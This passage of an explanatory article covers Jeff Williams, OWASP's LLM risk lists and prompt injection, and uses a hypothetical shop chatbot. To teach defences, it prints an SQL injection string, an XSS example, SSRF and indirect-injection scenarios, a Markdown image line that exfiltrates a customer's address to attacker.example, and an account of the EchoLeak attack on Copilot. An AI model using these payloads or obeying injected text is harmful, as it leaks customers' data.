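# Jeff Williams on prompt injection and security flaws in applications built on large language models

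## Who Jeff Williams is and what injection means in application security

Jeff Williams is a specialist in application security, which deals with flaws in programs rather than in networks or machines. He helped found OWASP, the Open Worldwide Application Security Project, a nonprofit community that publishes free guidance and tools. He led the drafting of its best-known document, the Top 10 list of web vulnerabilities. He co-founded Contrast Security, which sells software for finding flaws and blocking attacks inside running applications, and is now its chief technology officer.

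Since the release of ChatGPT in late 2022, developers have been connecting their programs to large language models (LLMs), the systems behind such chatbots. OWASP ranks prompt injection, in which an attacker writes text that the model follows as if it were a legitimate instruction, first among the risks of these programs. Williams's field has long used the word "injection" for older flaws, and programmers have reliable remedies for those. Much of the debate about LLM security is about how far those remedies also work against prompt injection.

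### Williams's work before language models

Williams came to security by accident in 1992, while working on the user interface of a US Navy system that had strict security requirements. *User:Jeff Williams*, a profile on OWASP's old wiki that he last revised in 2015, also describes his research project on the first version of Java. Java ran code inside a "sandbox" meant to limit what the code could do, and Williams thought that some attacks might get around it. So he wrote a class loader (the component that brings code into a running Java program) that altered the code as it loaded. Every security-relevant call then had to pass a checkpoint that the original code did not control. Contrast's products use a related technique, and Williams's advice on AI agents follows the same pattern.

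In April 2002, Williams, Dave Wichers, Noelle Hardy and others started Aspect Security, a consultancy that worked only on applications. Around that time, several government agencies told Williams that they knew application flaws were a problem but were basing their security work on the SANS Top 20, an existing list of security weaknesses. He wanted a top ten for applications, and a small team at Aspect took the lead in drafting one for OWASP. Ernst & Young later acquired Aspect, according to GetPodcast's *About Jeff Williams*.

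The first OWASP Top 10 list came out in January 2003. Late on Sunday 12 January, Williams sent a security mailing list the press release that would go out the next morning, in an email titled *OWASP Identifies Ten Most Critical Web Application Security Vulnerabilities* (Williams, 2003). OWASP's *Top 10 2013* (2013) also gives 2003 as the year of first release. Steve Wilson, a colleague of Williams at Contrast in 2023, dates the first list to 2001 in *The OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications*, a chapter of his O'Reilly book on LLM security. That is too early if Aspect, which opened in April 2002, drafted the list.

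The press release argued that an organisation that puts an application on the web invites the whole world to send it requests. Attacks inside those requests pass the firewall because the requests are legal, so the application's own code becomes part of the security perimeter. This argument still matters for LLM applications. The first list began with "unvalidated parameters". *Open Source Group Issues Top Ten Web Vulnerabilities* (2003), a blog post from the same week, explained these as information from web requests that an application uses without checking it. Attackers could use this flaw to reach the systems behind the application.

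Williams chaired OWASP from 2003 to 2012 and set it up as a nonprofit foundation. His other projects there were mostly practical aids for programmers. WebGoat is a training environment that Aspect built for its courses and then donated, and the Enterprise Security API (ESAPI) is a library of ready-made security controls. He also wrote the XSS Prevention Cheat Sheet, a guide to preventing a browser attack called cross-site scripting. In the 2013 edition of the *OWASP Top 10*, Williams and Wichers urged readers to "stop chasing vulnerabilities" and instead establish strong controls, which can remove a whole class of flaw.

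### Injection in one database query

Injection is a flaw in which a program interprets an attacker's data as an instruction. The classic case involves SQL, the language in which programs put questions to databases. Suppose a shop's website asks for a customer's name and looks up the matching orders. A careless programmer builds the query by joining strings:

```
query = "SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = '" + name + "'"
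```

If the visitor types Smith, the database receives a request for all orders where the customer is 'Smith', as the programmer intended. An attacker types `x' OR '1'='1` instead, and the database receives this:

```
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = 'x' OR '1'='1'
```

The quotation mark after the x closes the name early, so the text after it becomes part of the command. Since '1'='1' is true for every row, the database returns every customer's orders. The database worked correctly, but it was a mistake to join a fixed command and untrusted text into one string, because the database cannot distinguish the programmer's characters from the rest.

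One response is to reject any name that contains a quotation mark. That shuts out customers called O'Brien, and it obliges the programmer to think of every dangerous input in advance. The better remedy is a parameterised query:

```
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = ?
```

The program gives the database this command with a placeholder where the name belongs, and supplies the name separately as a value. The command's structure is fixed before the database receives the name, so nothing a visitor types in the name field can change it, and the programmer does not need to recognise the attack. If the attacker types the same text as before, the database searches for a customer whose name is literally `x' OR '1'='1` and finds nobody.

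Security engineers call the form field a *source*, a place where untrusted data enters a program. The function call that runs the query is a *sink*, where that data can do harm. The *trust boundary* between them is the point where data passes from a less trusted part of a system to a more trusted one and the program has to check it. Here it lies between the visitor's browser, which the visitor controls, and the shop's server. Finding an injection flaw largely means tracing a path from a source to a sink along which nothing makes the data safe.

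The same input can also be dangerous at a different sink, such as a web page. Suppose the website replies "No orders found for" followed by whatever the visitor typed. If that text contains a `<script>` tag, the browser runs what follows as a program. This is cross-site scripting, or XSS, and an attacker who gets another person to open a link containing such a tag can run code in that person's browser. The remedy is *output encoding*, which rewrites text so that the receiving program treats it as data and not as code. For a web page, that means replacing `<` with `&lt;`, which the browser displays as an ordinary character. The right encoding depends on the receiver, because text that is harmless on a web page may be dangerous in a database query.

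### How text reaches a language model

An LLM application is software that sends text to a large language model and uses the reply. Its security matters more to organisations that build on a model than to people who occasionally ask a chatbot a question. The host of Software Engineering Radio's *Sourabh Satish on Prompt Injection* (2025) put this distinction to his guest at the start.

Suppose the shop adds a support chatbot, and a customer asks where a parcel is. The application starts with the system instructions, where the developer has told the model to discuss only orders and never reveal another customer's details. It adds the customer's question, then retrieves and adds any documents that may help, perhaps the order record and an email from the courier. The model receives all of this as one sequence of tokens, the word fragments it uses to process text. It predicts a likely next token,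 appends it to the sequence and repeats until the reply is complete.

Applications usually mark the source of each part of the model's input, and AI companies train their models to give system instructions more weight. But the markers are tokens in the same sequence, and the model has only a learned tendency to follow them, without the guarantee that a parameterised query gives. Harang (2024) said in *Practical LLM Security*, a talk at the Black Hat security conference, that an LLM has no intrinsic separation between control and data because "it's all fed into the same input". Harang argued that anyone who can provide input to the model can therefore influence its output.

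In the shop's case, that includes the courier or anyone who can send an email that looks like the courier's. Prompt injection is *direct* when the attacker types the text into the application, and *indirect* when the model reads it in a page, email or document. In an indirect attack, the customer may have done nothing careless. *Uncovering LLM Vulnerabilities*, by the testing team at the security consultancy Kroll, gives the example of an AI system that reads an email with hidden instructions and abandons its original task. Every document the application retrieves is therefore a potential source, in the sense of the SQL example, even though no visitor typed it into a form.

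### The origin of OWASP's list for LLM applications

In spring 2023 there was plenty of research on AI security, but little of it dealt with LLMs in an organised way. Wilson, then Contrast's chief product officer, began collecting papers and blog posts on LLMs and summarising them with ChatGPT. He then showed ChatGPT a few entries from the current web Top 10 and asked it for a similar list about LLMs. He writes in the O'Reilly chapter that he sent the result to Williams to find out whether it looked novel and worth pursuing, without saying that ChatGPT had written most of it. Williams encouraged him.

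Wilson had told the story closer to the event in *Steve Wilson -- OWASP Top Ten for LLMs*, an episode of The Application Security Podcast. He said he had written the draft "just for fun" and had been rather embarrassed to send it. He recalled Williams answering that it was better than the usual first cut of a top ten and that Wilson should submit it as an OWASP project. Williams's reply is known only from his colleague Wilson's paraphrases, which don't include his opinion of any particular entry.

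Two weeks into an eight-week plan, Wilson counted 260 people in the project's working group, and about 170 had joined the opening call. OWASP (2023) published a preview, version 0.5, on 1 July, with Wilson as project lead and more than 370 members. Prompt injection came first on the list. OWASP introduced a revised edition in November 2024 and started a separate initiative on AI agents the following month.

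### Which statements are Williams's own

Williams has made few statements about LLM applications, all of them recent. The fullest is an interview of 17 September 2026, *Stop Studying the Robot's Brain. Start Controlling Its Body* (Smith, 2026). It discusses the agent harness, which is the tools, memory, permissions and orchestration around a model that let it act. He appears to have published no signed article, talk or post on prompt injection between 2023 and 2025. The posts on his Contrast Security author page, *Jeff Williams, Co-Founder, Chief Technology Officer*, cover topics such as API security and legal liability for insecure software.

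He has spoken more often about AI as a tool for writing, attacking and repairing ordinary software. In April 2026, on Cybersecurity Today's *AI-Powered AppSec, OWASP Origins, and Anthropic's "Mythos" Model*, he discussed an Anthropic model that is good at finding unknown vulnerabilities, and the discussion also covered why finding more bugs helps only if repair improves too. OWASP (2026) listed him for a conference debate on 6 November about whether automatic repair weakens developers' responsibility for their own code. These subjects are related to prompt injection, but it arises only in programs that contain a model, and a program written with AI's help need not contain one.

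Most of what Contrast said about LLM applications in 2023 came from people other than Williams. Wilson spoke for the OWASP project and gave his own views on prompt injection. David Lindner, the company's chief information security officer, responded to the draft list in Contrast Security's *A CISO’s response to OWASP’s Top 10 Generative AI vulnerabilities*, where he guessed that about half of the ten problems had no solution yet. In August, Contrast Security (2023) announced a rule for detecting prompt injection weaknesses in code that uses OpenAI's models. As chief technology officer, Williams may well have contributed to that product, but neither the announcement nor his colleagues' remarks can be taken as his own opinion.

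He also has a commercial interest in the answer. Contrast sells runtime instrumentation, sensors inside a running application that observe its data flows and actions. Asked in *Why Runtime Insight, Not Just Scans, Unlocks Real AppSec Protection* (Pandagle, 2025) which security tools he would recommend, Williams said that a security chief should first install application detection and response, a category of product that Contrast sells. Yet as OWASP's chair he had made rules to stop vendors from marketing their products through its conferences and chapters, and had complained of companies that claimed to "address the OWASP Top Ten". Contrast itself promoted its 2023 rule as a way to address the top entry on OWASP's LLM list, a project that Contrast's chief product officer led.

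None of this makes his technical arguments wrong. His interest in checking what code does as it runs goes back to the Java class loader, years before Contrast had a product, and anyone can test his arguments against how LLM applications work. But Williams says the industry should worry less about the model and more about what the software around it can do, and his company could benefit if the industry agrees. On that point, evidence from people who don't sell such products deserves more weight than his word.

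## Prompt injection compared with SQL injection

Developers can use a parameterised query to make a database treat an attacker's text as data. They can't rely on a language model to do this, which is one reason to follow Williams's advice and concentrate on the software around the model.

Customers type questions into a chat window on the shop's website. To answer them, the chatbot can look up orders in the shop's database and read the emails that customers and couriers send to the support address. The model has no database connection, so it writes a request in a fixed format, such as a lookup of a certain order number. The application carries out the lookup and adds the result to the model's input. It does this through a single database account that can read every customer's orders.

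### Direct and indirect attacks on the chatbot

In a direct injection, the attacker uses the ordinary customer chat window to ask about somebody else's order. The message also includes text to make the request look legitimate, such as a claim that the shop's staff are testing the system. If the model gives this text more weight than the developer's instruction to protect other customers' details, it writes a lookup request for that order. The application carries out the request, and the chatbot shows the attacker that customer's address.

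The attacker's message crosses a trust boundary when it passes from the browser to the shop's server, as the typed name did in the SQL example. Another boundary lies between the model and the database. Once the model has read the message, its output deserves no more trust than the message, yet the application acts on the model's lookup request as if the developer had written it.

An indirect injection does not require the attacker to use the chat window. For example, the attacker sends the support address an email that looks like a courier's notice about an order but includes a passage addressed to the model. Days later, the real customer asks where the parcel is. The chatbot retrieves the emails about the order, and the model processes the attacker's passage together with the customer's question. The chatbot then tells the customer that delivery will resume after a small payment, and links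 to a page that the attacker controls.

Here the untrusted text crosses the first boundary when the application copies the email into the model's input. A developer can easily overlook this because the email comes from the shop's own mailbox. The second crossing happens when the reply goes to a customer who trusts the shop. Staff who open the email may notice nothing odd. OWASP (2023) noted in version 1.1 of its LLM list that the injected text need not be visible to people as long as the software parses it.

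OWASP called a model that an attacker manipulates in this way a "confused deputy", an old computer security term for a program that someone tricks into using its legitimate authority on their behalf. The attacker has no right to read the order database, but the chatbot does. When the attack works, the database receives a valid query from a valid account, so its access checks don't stop it. OWASP used the term for indirect injection, but it fits the direct attack on the shop equally well.

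### What Contrast's 2023 rule establishes

On 3 August 2023, Contrast Security applied a classic method, tracing data from source to sink, to prompt injection. Its rule fires when a Python application carrying Contrast's sensors sends user input to a model through OpenAI's official Python API. Wilson, the only person quoted in the announcement, said that organisations could now "identify susceptible data flows to their LLMs". The company made the broader claim that its product was "ideal for identifying all types of injection accurately", including prompt injection.

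In simplified form, the shop's chatbot might contain these lines:

```
question = request.form["question"]
prompt = instructions + question
reply = ask_model(prompt)
```

Runtime tools generally trace such a flow by marking data. When the first line reads the customer's question from the web request, a sensor marks the text as untrusted. The second line joins the question to the developer's instructions, and the mark carries over to the new string. The third line passes that string to the library that sends it to the model. A sensor there checks for marked text and reports the path from source to sink if it finds any.

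Such a report is good evidence that untrusted text can reach the model by this route, because the tool recorded it happening in a running program. A scanner that only reads source code has to infer it.

Finding marked text inside a database command comes close to proving a flaw, because it means the programmer has left out a known remedy, the parameterised query. Switching to one clears the finding. That kind of fix isn't available for a support chatbot, because its purpose is to send customers' questions to a model. As Contrast described the rule, it would flag a carelessly built chatbot, a well-defended one, and one with no access to orders or anything else of value.

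The finding therefore shows that an attacker can put text in front of the model at that point, but it does not prove that anyone can exploit this. That depends on whether the model would follow the text and what the application would then do, and the trace stops before either. Elsewhere in the announcement, Contrast wrote of "potential prompt injection vulnerabilities", which describes the finding better than its claim of accuracy does.

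It is still useful to know which programs are exposed, because many teams in a large company may have added calls to a model, and security staff can't protect programs they don't know about. But the first version of the rule could find only some of these programs, since it covered one company's models and one programming language. Contrast also listed websites, emails and documents as ways an injection can arrive, but didn't state whether the rule counted text from them as user input. If it didn't, the rule would flag the shop's chat window and miss the false courier's email.

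### Why a model has no parameterised query

Prompt injection has the same cause as SQL injection. In both cases, a developer joins trusted and untrusted text, and the attacker's data ends up working as an instruction. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives an example in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, which the centre published in December 2025. A recruitment system uses a model to score CVs, and a candidate hides a line of text telling the model to approve the application. The post mainly argues that the comparison with SQL injection is dangerous because it leads people who know web security to expect the same kind of cure.

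A parameterised query prevents SQL injection because the database engine already handles commands and values differently. David C wrote that inside a model "there is only ever 'next token'". Special training, source markers and attack detectors all add a distinction between instructions and data that the underlying technology does not make.

Charles Ye, Jasmine Cui and Dylan Hadfield-Menell have studied how weak the markers are, in work that the software developer Simon Willison summarised in June 2026. They found that models seem to give more weight to the style of a text than to the tags that identify its source. When they added a passage in the style of a model's private reasoning to a user's message, models such as gpt-oss-20b could treat the passage as their own reasoning and act against their training, even though the message was correctly tagged.

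Filtering is also harder than it is for SQL. Only a limited set of characters and keywords has special meaning in a database command, but there are endless ways to phrase a request in English. David C therefore warned against blocking known phrases. Some successful attacks don't look like attacks. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an email from 2025 that resembles a routine message about a restructuring and asks the reader's AI assistant to submit an employee's details to a "compliance validation system". In testing, it worked half the time. The same input to the same SQL query normally has the same effect on every attempt, but a developer who sees a prompt injection fail once can't assume it will fail again.

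David C preferred to think of the model as a confused deputy. Programmers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, for instance by making it check whose request it is carrying out. But an LLM is "inherently confusable", so an organisation can reduce the likelihood and damage of an attack but can't eliminate the risk. If it can't tolerate what remains, the task may not suit an LLM. David C feared a repeat of the history of SQL injection, which became rare in websites only after a decade of breaches led to better defaults.

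### What the comparison still offers designers

OpenAI's engineers still use source and sink analysis for ChatGPT, along with lessons from how companies protect employees against deception. In their version, a source is any way an attacker can influence the system, and a sink is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context, such as sending information to a third party.

OpenAI's analysis places the sink at the action that follows the model's output, whereas Contrast's rule ended the trace at the model. In the shop, the false courier's email is a source, and the order lookup and the reply to the customer are possible sinks. The designer assumes that the model may sometimes pass the attacker's instruction from source to sink, and looks for a point on the path where ordinary code can intervene. OpenAI made the same point with the example of a human support worker who can grant refunds.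 The employer expects some customers to lie, so a separate system limits how much the worker can pay out.

Other guidance is similar. In its 2023 list, OWASP acknowledged that there was "no fool-proof prevention within the LLM" and advised developers to treat the model as an untrusted user, with trust boundaries between it, outside sources and the functions it can call. Frontier Model Forum, an industry body, recommends in its 2026 brief *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* that companies deploying agents use established controls, such as restricting access and checking inputs and outputs.

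David C also wanted safeguards in ordinary code that constrain what the system can do, so the disagreement is narrower than the post's title suggests. The SQL comparison helps a designer find dangerous paths but misleads anyone who hopes to close them inside the model. For prompt injection, the strong controls that Williams and Wichers recommended in 2013 must be in the code around the model.

### How often current models resist

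Even without a guarantee, a model that almost always ignored injected text would make the shop much safer. AI companies have made fast progress on this. OpenAI tests its models with GPT-Red, an automated attacker that it also uses in training. In September 2026, it published results for GPT-6 Astra in its *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) and compared them with those for the model's predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol. The older model's figure for direct attacks comes from TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026).

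| Share of attacks that succeeded | GPT-5.6 Sol | GPT-6 Astra |
|---|---|---|
| Direct attacks by GPT-Red, per query | about 0.05% | 0.01% |
| Indirect attacks by GPT-Red, per query | 3.77% | 0.21% |
| Gray Swan's indirect attacks, at least one success in 15 attempts | 27.0% | 8.5% |

The last row comes from an outside test by Gray Swan, a company that specialises in attacking AI systems. The test used 1,810 attacks selected from competitions held in 2026, in which competitors injected text to try to make an agent steal or destroy data, compromise a system or move money. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026), who include staff of OpenAI, Anthropic, Meta and the British and American government AI institutes, describe a large public competition of this kind.

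The outside result is so much worse partly because Gray Swan's measure allows the attacker fifteen attempts and counts a single success as a failure of the model, and because Astra was trained on the kind of attacks GPT-Red uses. The outside figure is probably the better guide for the shop, since anyone can send its support address fifteen emails. Even at the lower rate of 0.21%, about one indirect attack in 480 succeeds.

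The shop might also choose a cheaper model. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) reports that GPT-6 Sol resists 97.13% of indirect attacks and GPT-6 Luna resists 95.80%. These numbers are second-hand, from a blog's analysis of OpenAI's system card. If they are right, more than ten times as many attacks get through as with Astra.

Anthropic's models have also become harder to attack. Anthropic calls Claude Mythos 5.1 its most robust model so far on an external benchmark of indirect injection. Willison reported in August 2026 that none of 720 attempts succeeded against three other recent Claude models in a test Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs. The attempts covered 72 scenarios that the testers had kept from Anthropic. The models ran in Claude Code, Anthropic's programming tool, in a mode where an additional check can block dangerous actions, so the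 result measures the models and that safeguard together. Willison wanted more independent confirmation.

An informal contest came closer to the shop's situation. Fernando Irarrázaval invited people to email an AI assistant and try to make it reveal a secret. The assistant ran on Claude Opus 4.6, an older model, and was told never to disclose credentials in response to an email. About 2,000 people made 6,000 attempts, and all failed. If those attempts were independent and typical of future ones, the true success rate would very probably be below one in 2,000. But a skilled attacker is not a typical contestant, and Willison still advised against using such a system where an injection could do irreversible damage. Research on adaptive attacks, in which the attacker revises the text after each failure, supports that caution. OpenAI found that GPT-Red could defeat the older GPT-5.1 in 84% of scenarios,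 compared with 13% for human testers.

Ariel Fogel, an OWASP contributor and researcher at the security company Pillar Security, judged in June 2026 that prompt injection remained unsolved at the architectural level. *Prompt Injection Remains Unsolved, OWASP Researcher Warns* (Poireault, 2026) reported Fogel's reasoning from the Infosecurity Europe conference that a model receives everything in one sequence of tokens, so it has no reliable way to enforce different privileges for the developer, the user and retrieved content. This was Fogel's own view, not an OWASP ruling, and an employee of a security company has an interest in the problem. But David C, who works for a government agency, reached much the same conclusion.

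OpenAI and Anthropic published results later that summer showing that attacks succeed less often. These results don't refute Fogel's claim, which is about a boundary that would hold against every input, as a parameterised query does. Fogel wanted defenders to put more effort into limiting what an agent can do after an injection succeeds, and Williams also emphasises this.

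## Model output as untrusted input and the leakage of data

When an injection succeeds, the harm comes from what the application does with the model's reply. The false courier's email in the shop's mailbox can only change the text the model produces; it can't run code or open a database connection. The application then displays that text, puts it in a query or follows an address in it.

Because an attacker's input can shape a model's output, OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* compares passing on unchecked output to giving users "indirect access to additional functionality". Developers should treat the model's replies like text from a stranger, even though they chose the model. This applies even without an attacker. Harang pointed out that a model picks its tokens partly at random, so an unlikely output will occur sooner or later, and concluded that the model should always be inside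 its own security boundary.

### One reply at three sinks

Suppose the shop's application inserts each reply directly into the chat window's web page. In the email, the attacker asks the model to include a `<script>` tag when it summarises the delivery. If the model includes the tag, the customer's browser runs the attacker's code as part of the shop's website. This is cross-site scripting carried out through the model, and the usual defence, output encoding, prevents it.

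Chatbots complicate this remedy a little because their replies often contain Markdown, a simple notation for bold text, lists, links and images, which the application converts into HTML. If the application encoded that HTML, customers would see tags instead of formatting. Developers usually convert the reply first and then pass it through a sanitiser, which removes everything except a short list of harmless tags. OWASP also recommends a Content Security Policy, which specifies the scripts and other resources a browser may load on a website.

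The model's order lookups reach a different sink, the database. A careless programmer might build the query from the order number in the model's request:

```
query = "SELECT status FROM orders WHERE number = '" + order_number + "'"
```

An attacker who gets the model to supply `x' OR '1'='1` as the number has carried out an SQL injection without typing anything into a form. A parameterised query stops this, and it can also limit whose orders the application looks up:

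```
SELECT status FROM orders WHERE number = ? AND customer_id = ?
```

The application fills the first placeholder with the model's value and the second with the customer's identity from the login session. Without the condition on `customer_id`, the query would be safe from SQL injection but would still return another customer's order if the model supplied that order's number.

This works because the model supplies only a value. Some applications let the model write the whole query, so that staff can question a database in plain English. Placeholders can't help then, because the untrusted text is the command. OWASP describes a model that writes a query deleting every table. The developer can limit the model to a few fixed queries, or run its queries through a read-only account with access to a limited set of records.

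The third sink is a request to another server. Suppose the chatbot checks a parcel's status by giving the application the address of a tracking page to fetch. An attacker gets the model to supply an address inside the shop's network instead, perhaps an administration page that the firewall hides from the internet. The request comes from the shop's server, so the firewall doesn't block it. Security engineers call this server-side request forgery, or SSRF.

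Encoding doesn't help here, because the address is well formed but points to the wrong place. The application needs a list of allowed destinations, in this case the courier's servers, and must check the new address against that list if a server redirects the request. An even safer design lets the model supply only a tracking number and has ordinary code build the address. In 2023, OWASP described a related attack on a weather plugin that accepts a web address. A malicious user points the plugin to their own server, whose response injects more text into the model.

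### The cheat sheet's rule applied to model output

Williams's XSS Prevention Cheat Sheet has separate rules for untrusted text in the body of a web page, in a tag's attributes, in a script, in a style sheet and in a link's address. Replacing `<` with `&lt;` protects the body, but not a link whose address begins with `javascript:`, which the browser may run as code when someone clicks it. The programmer therefore has to know where the text is going before choosing how to make it safe.

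Williams wrote the guide for web pages, so extending this rule to language models is an inference. But OWASP's 2025 entry similarly recommends "context-aware output encoding" that depends on where the application will use the reply.

A filter placed directly after the model therefore can't make a reply permanently safe. If the shop stores the chatbot's replies and later shows them on a page for staff, or copies them into an email, the application has to encode them again for the new destination. The same applies to programmers' tools that show replies in a text terminal. Terminals process ANSI escape sequences, short codes that change colours or move the cursor, which are harmless on a web page. The 2026 edition of OWASP's list now covers these codes, according to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026).

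### Output handling and disclosure in OWASP's lists

OWASP published that edition, the third, in August 2026. The table compares the 2023 list with the 2025 ranking in Barracuda's *OWASP Top 10 Risks for Large Language Models* and the 2026 ranking reported by SC Media.

| Risk | 2023 | 2025 | 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Output handling ("insecure", later "improper") | 2nd | 5th | 10th |
| Sensitive information disclosure | 6th | 2nd | 2nd |
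| System prompt leakage, later hidden context exposure | no separate entry | 7th | 8th |
| Vector and embedding weaknesses, which affect retrieval | no separate entry | 8th | 9th |

For the 2026 edition, OWASP checked its members' votes against 7,714 recorded incidents from public vulnerability databases, 6,639 of them detailed enough to classify. Votes carried three-quarters of the weight in the ranking. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* reported that votes and incidents agreed closely on sensitive information disclosure, which ranked second. That agreement makes its position better supported than most, although a leak from a company's private chatbot may never reach a public database.

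Output handling fell further than any other entry in OWASP's ranking. Invicti, which sells tools for testing web applications, attributes the drop to the other risks becoming more urgent, not to this one becoming less so. That is plausible, because a ranking shows only relative importance and OWASP widened the entry's scope at the same time. The low rank is not a good reason for developers to put off the work, since cross-site scripting and SQL injection through a model, unlike prompt injection, have reliable fixes that take little effort.

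### Secrets and personal data in the model's input

The shop's developer might write the password for the courier's booking system into the system instructions so that the chatbot can arrange returns, and tell the model never to reveal it. A customer may still persuade the model to repeat the password. OWASP warned in 2023 that a model might not follow such restrictions. The 2026 list extends the warning to all hidden context, including descriptions of the model's tools and internal policy text. An SC Media article produced with OWASP's project reports the advice to assume that outsiders can discover this material and to keep passwords and other credentials out of it.

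The shop's application can store the password itself and add it to the booking request after the model outputs a request for a return. No injection can then extract the password from the model, because the model never receives it. Ordinary code should likewise enforce hidden rules, such as a maximum refund, so that a customer who discovers them gains little.

Personal data can leave the shop without any attack. Unless the shop runs a model on its own machines, every question goes to an outside provider, along with the order record and emails the application retrieved. In 2023, OWASP warned that unclear terms could let a provider train its models on such data, and gave the example of a provider that changes its terms so that customers have to opt out. A model trained on the data might later reproduce it for somebody else.

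In September 2023, Contrast released an AI policy for other organisations to use. One of its rules bans letting public AI systems learn from proprietary data, according to Tech Newsday's *Contrast Security open source AI policy to protect privacy and security* (2023).

A contract can forbid training and limit how long the provider keeps the data, but the data still leaves the shop. To send less, the application can drop the fields the model doesn't need before each call and replace the customer's name and address with placeholders, then put the real details back when the reply arrives. This works well for an order record with fixed fields but is less reliable for free text, where a customer may mention an illness or a neighbour's name.

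### Lindner's view and retrieval that respects access rights

In a 2023 post by Contrast Security, the company's security chief, Lindner, asked about sensitive data in a chatbot, "How do you control the access?" and answered, "You can't." His example was a company that trains a model on all its customer data. He thought using only public data would defeat the purpose, so he suggested a layer in front of the model to check what goes in and what comes out. Williams doesn't appear in the post.

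Lindner's argument was strong for data inside a trained model. Training adjusts the numbers that make up the model, and nothing in those numbers records which customer may see which fact. In 2023, OWASP advised against training a model on privileged information that it might then display to users with fewer rights. Lindner's checking layer would catch some leaks, but it would have to recognise private information in free text, which the model can phrase in many different ways.

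Retrieval gives developers more control, because the data stays in a database or document store and the application fetches only a few passages for each question. In the same post, Lindner described how an ordinary program establishes who has logged in and then queries for that person's account. A retrieval system can do this before it calls the model. The shop's application would take the customer's identity from the login session, search only that customer's orders and emails, and add nothing else to the model's input. An injection might still make the model misuse those records, but it couldn't extract another customer's, because the model would never have received them. Lindner's "You can't" is therefore too pessimistic for retrieval.

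The shop's chatbot doesn't yet have this protection, since it uses a single account that can read every order. OWASP listed the same mistake in 2023, giving the example of a plugin that fetches one user's documents through an account that can open everybody's. The developer has to run each search with the customer's access rights, or add a filter that the model can't remove.

Many retrieval systems search by comparing embeddings, which are lists of numbers that represent the meaning of a text. According to SC Media's report on the 2026 list, when several customers share such a system, an attacker may be able to infer things about other customers' documents despite authentication controls. A separate index for each customer would reduce that risk but cost more and take more work to maintain.

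Williams's remarks to Smith in September 2026 support the same division of work between model and application. He said the rules on what an agent can do "should live outside the brain", meaning outside the model. He was talking about agents' permissions, not retrieval or output encoding, so applying his remarks to customer records is again an inference.

### Replies that send data to an attacker

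A customer's access rights offer no protection when the reply itself sends that customer's data elsewhere. Suppose the false courier's email gets the model to end its answer with this line:

```
![parcel](https://attacker.example/p.png?address=12+Mill+Lane)
```

This is Markdown for an image. As soon as the chat window displays the reply, the browser requests the picture from the attacker's server and sends the customer's address with the request. The customer may notice only a missing picture. OWASP described this attack in 2023, but in its example the leaked data was a summary of a private conversation.

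Encoding or a sanitiser that permits images may not stop it, because the line contains no code and the chat window is supposed to show images. The shop needs a list of allowed destinations here too. The application can remove every image that doesn't come from the shop's own server, and a Content Security Policy can make the browser block any it misses.

Link previews create a similar problem in chat programs, which may fetch a page as soon as someone posts a link to it. Willison noted in 2024 that a chatbot subjected to prompt injection could leak private data in this way. He passed on a tip from the security researcher Johann Rehberger that applications posting to Slack can turn the previews off.

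Researchers demonstrated the image attack in 2025 against Copilot, Microsoft's AI assistant for office work, and called it EchoLeak. They sent an email that seemed to be written for a person and never mentioned Copilot. When the recipient later asked Copilot about something else, the assistant retrieved the email as background, followed its instructions and put sensitive internal data into the address of an image. The browser fetched the image without a click. Wiz's *OWASP LLM top 10* describes EchoLeak as the first confirmed attack of its kind to work on a live product without any action by the user, and reports that Microsoft patched the flaw in May 2025.

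EchoLeak was a demonstration, and no theft through it is known. Attackers are also trying prompt injection outside the laboratory. Wiz reports that the security company Forcepoint catalogued ten examples in circulation in April 2026, though this count doesn't show how many succeeded.

Copilot had a classifier to detect injected instructions, a filter for links and a Content Security Policy, and the attack got past all of them. Checking the recipient's access rights wouldn't have helped either if the recipient was entitled to read the files. A list of allowed servers also fails if one of those servers will fetch any address on request, because an attacker can use it as a relay. The developer therefore has to check what each server does with a request before adding it to the list.

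## Keeping permissions outside the model and watching what the application does

Williams thinks the security industry spends too much effort on whether someone can trick a model into producing something dangerous. In his September 2026 interview with Smith, he said that once a model can act, a much more important question is "what can the robot actually do?" He wants ordinary software to limit an agent's actions and companies to monitor what the agent does within those limits.

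### The robot's brain and its body

Williams compares the model to a robot's brain and the agent harness to its body. He imagines the same brain in two bodies, one with only a camera and a speaker, and the other with access to email, production systems, corporate databases and a credit card. The two robots are equally intelligent but carry very different risks, so he calls it "increasingly meaningless" to evaluate an agent by its model alone.

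The harness has several parts, and the shop's chatbot has simple versions of most of them. Context and data are the robot's senses, and the chatbot's are the order records and emails. Memory is what the robot retains from experience, such as any notes the application keeps from a customer's earlier chats. Tools are its hands, and the chatbot's tool is the order lookup. Orchestration is its nervous system, the code that passes the model's requests to the tools and returns the results. Identity and permissions determine which doors the robot can open. The chatbot's database account opens too many because it can read every customer's orders.

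Williams was most emphatic about permissions. He told Smith, "I don't want the robot's brain deciding its own permissions," and said that "every attempt to do this has been circumvented". A developer who writes "never refund more than £50" in the system instructions makes this mistake, because the limit holds only if the model follows it. Williams would rather physically stop a robot from opening a vault than tell it not to. Software outside the model should determine whether an agent can run code, send email or transfer money, and should require approval for sensitive actions.

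"Every attempt" is too sweeping. Irarrázaval's email assistant was protecting its secret with an instruction, and nobody extracted it. But Williams's argument depends only on the weaker claim that no instruction is certain to work, and David C's account of how models process text supports that.

Testing the model is also still worthwhile. In the same harness, GPT-6 Astra would let through about one-eighteenth as many of GPT-Red's indirect attacks as its predecessor would.

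Others share Williams's concern. The day before Williams's interview appeared, Constantin (2026) reported in *The hardest AI security problems...* that OWASP had moved "excessive agency" from sixth to third on its LLM list. The term covers applications that give a model more functions, permissions or independence than its task requires. In May, the cybersecurity agencies of the Five Eyes countries, which have no product to sell, issued guidance on AI agents. Trent (2026), in *Operationalizing the OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications*, summarises their advice to start with low-risk tasks, give agents the fewest privileges they need, keep people overseeing them and contain the damage when they misbehave.

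### One injection against three chatbots

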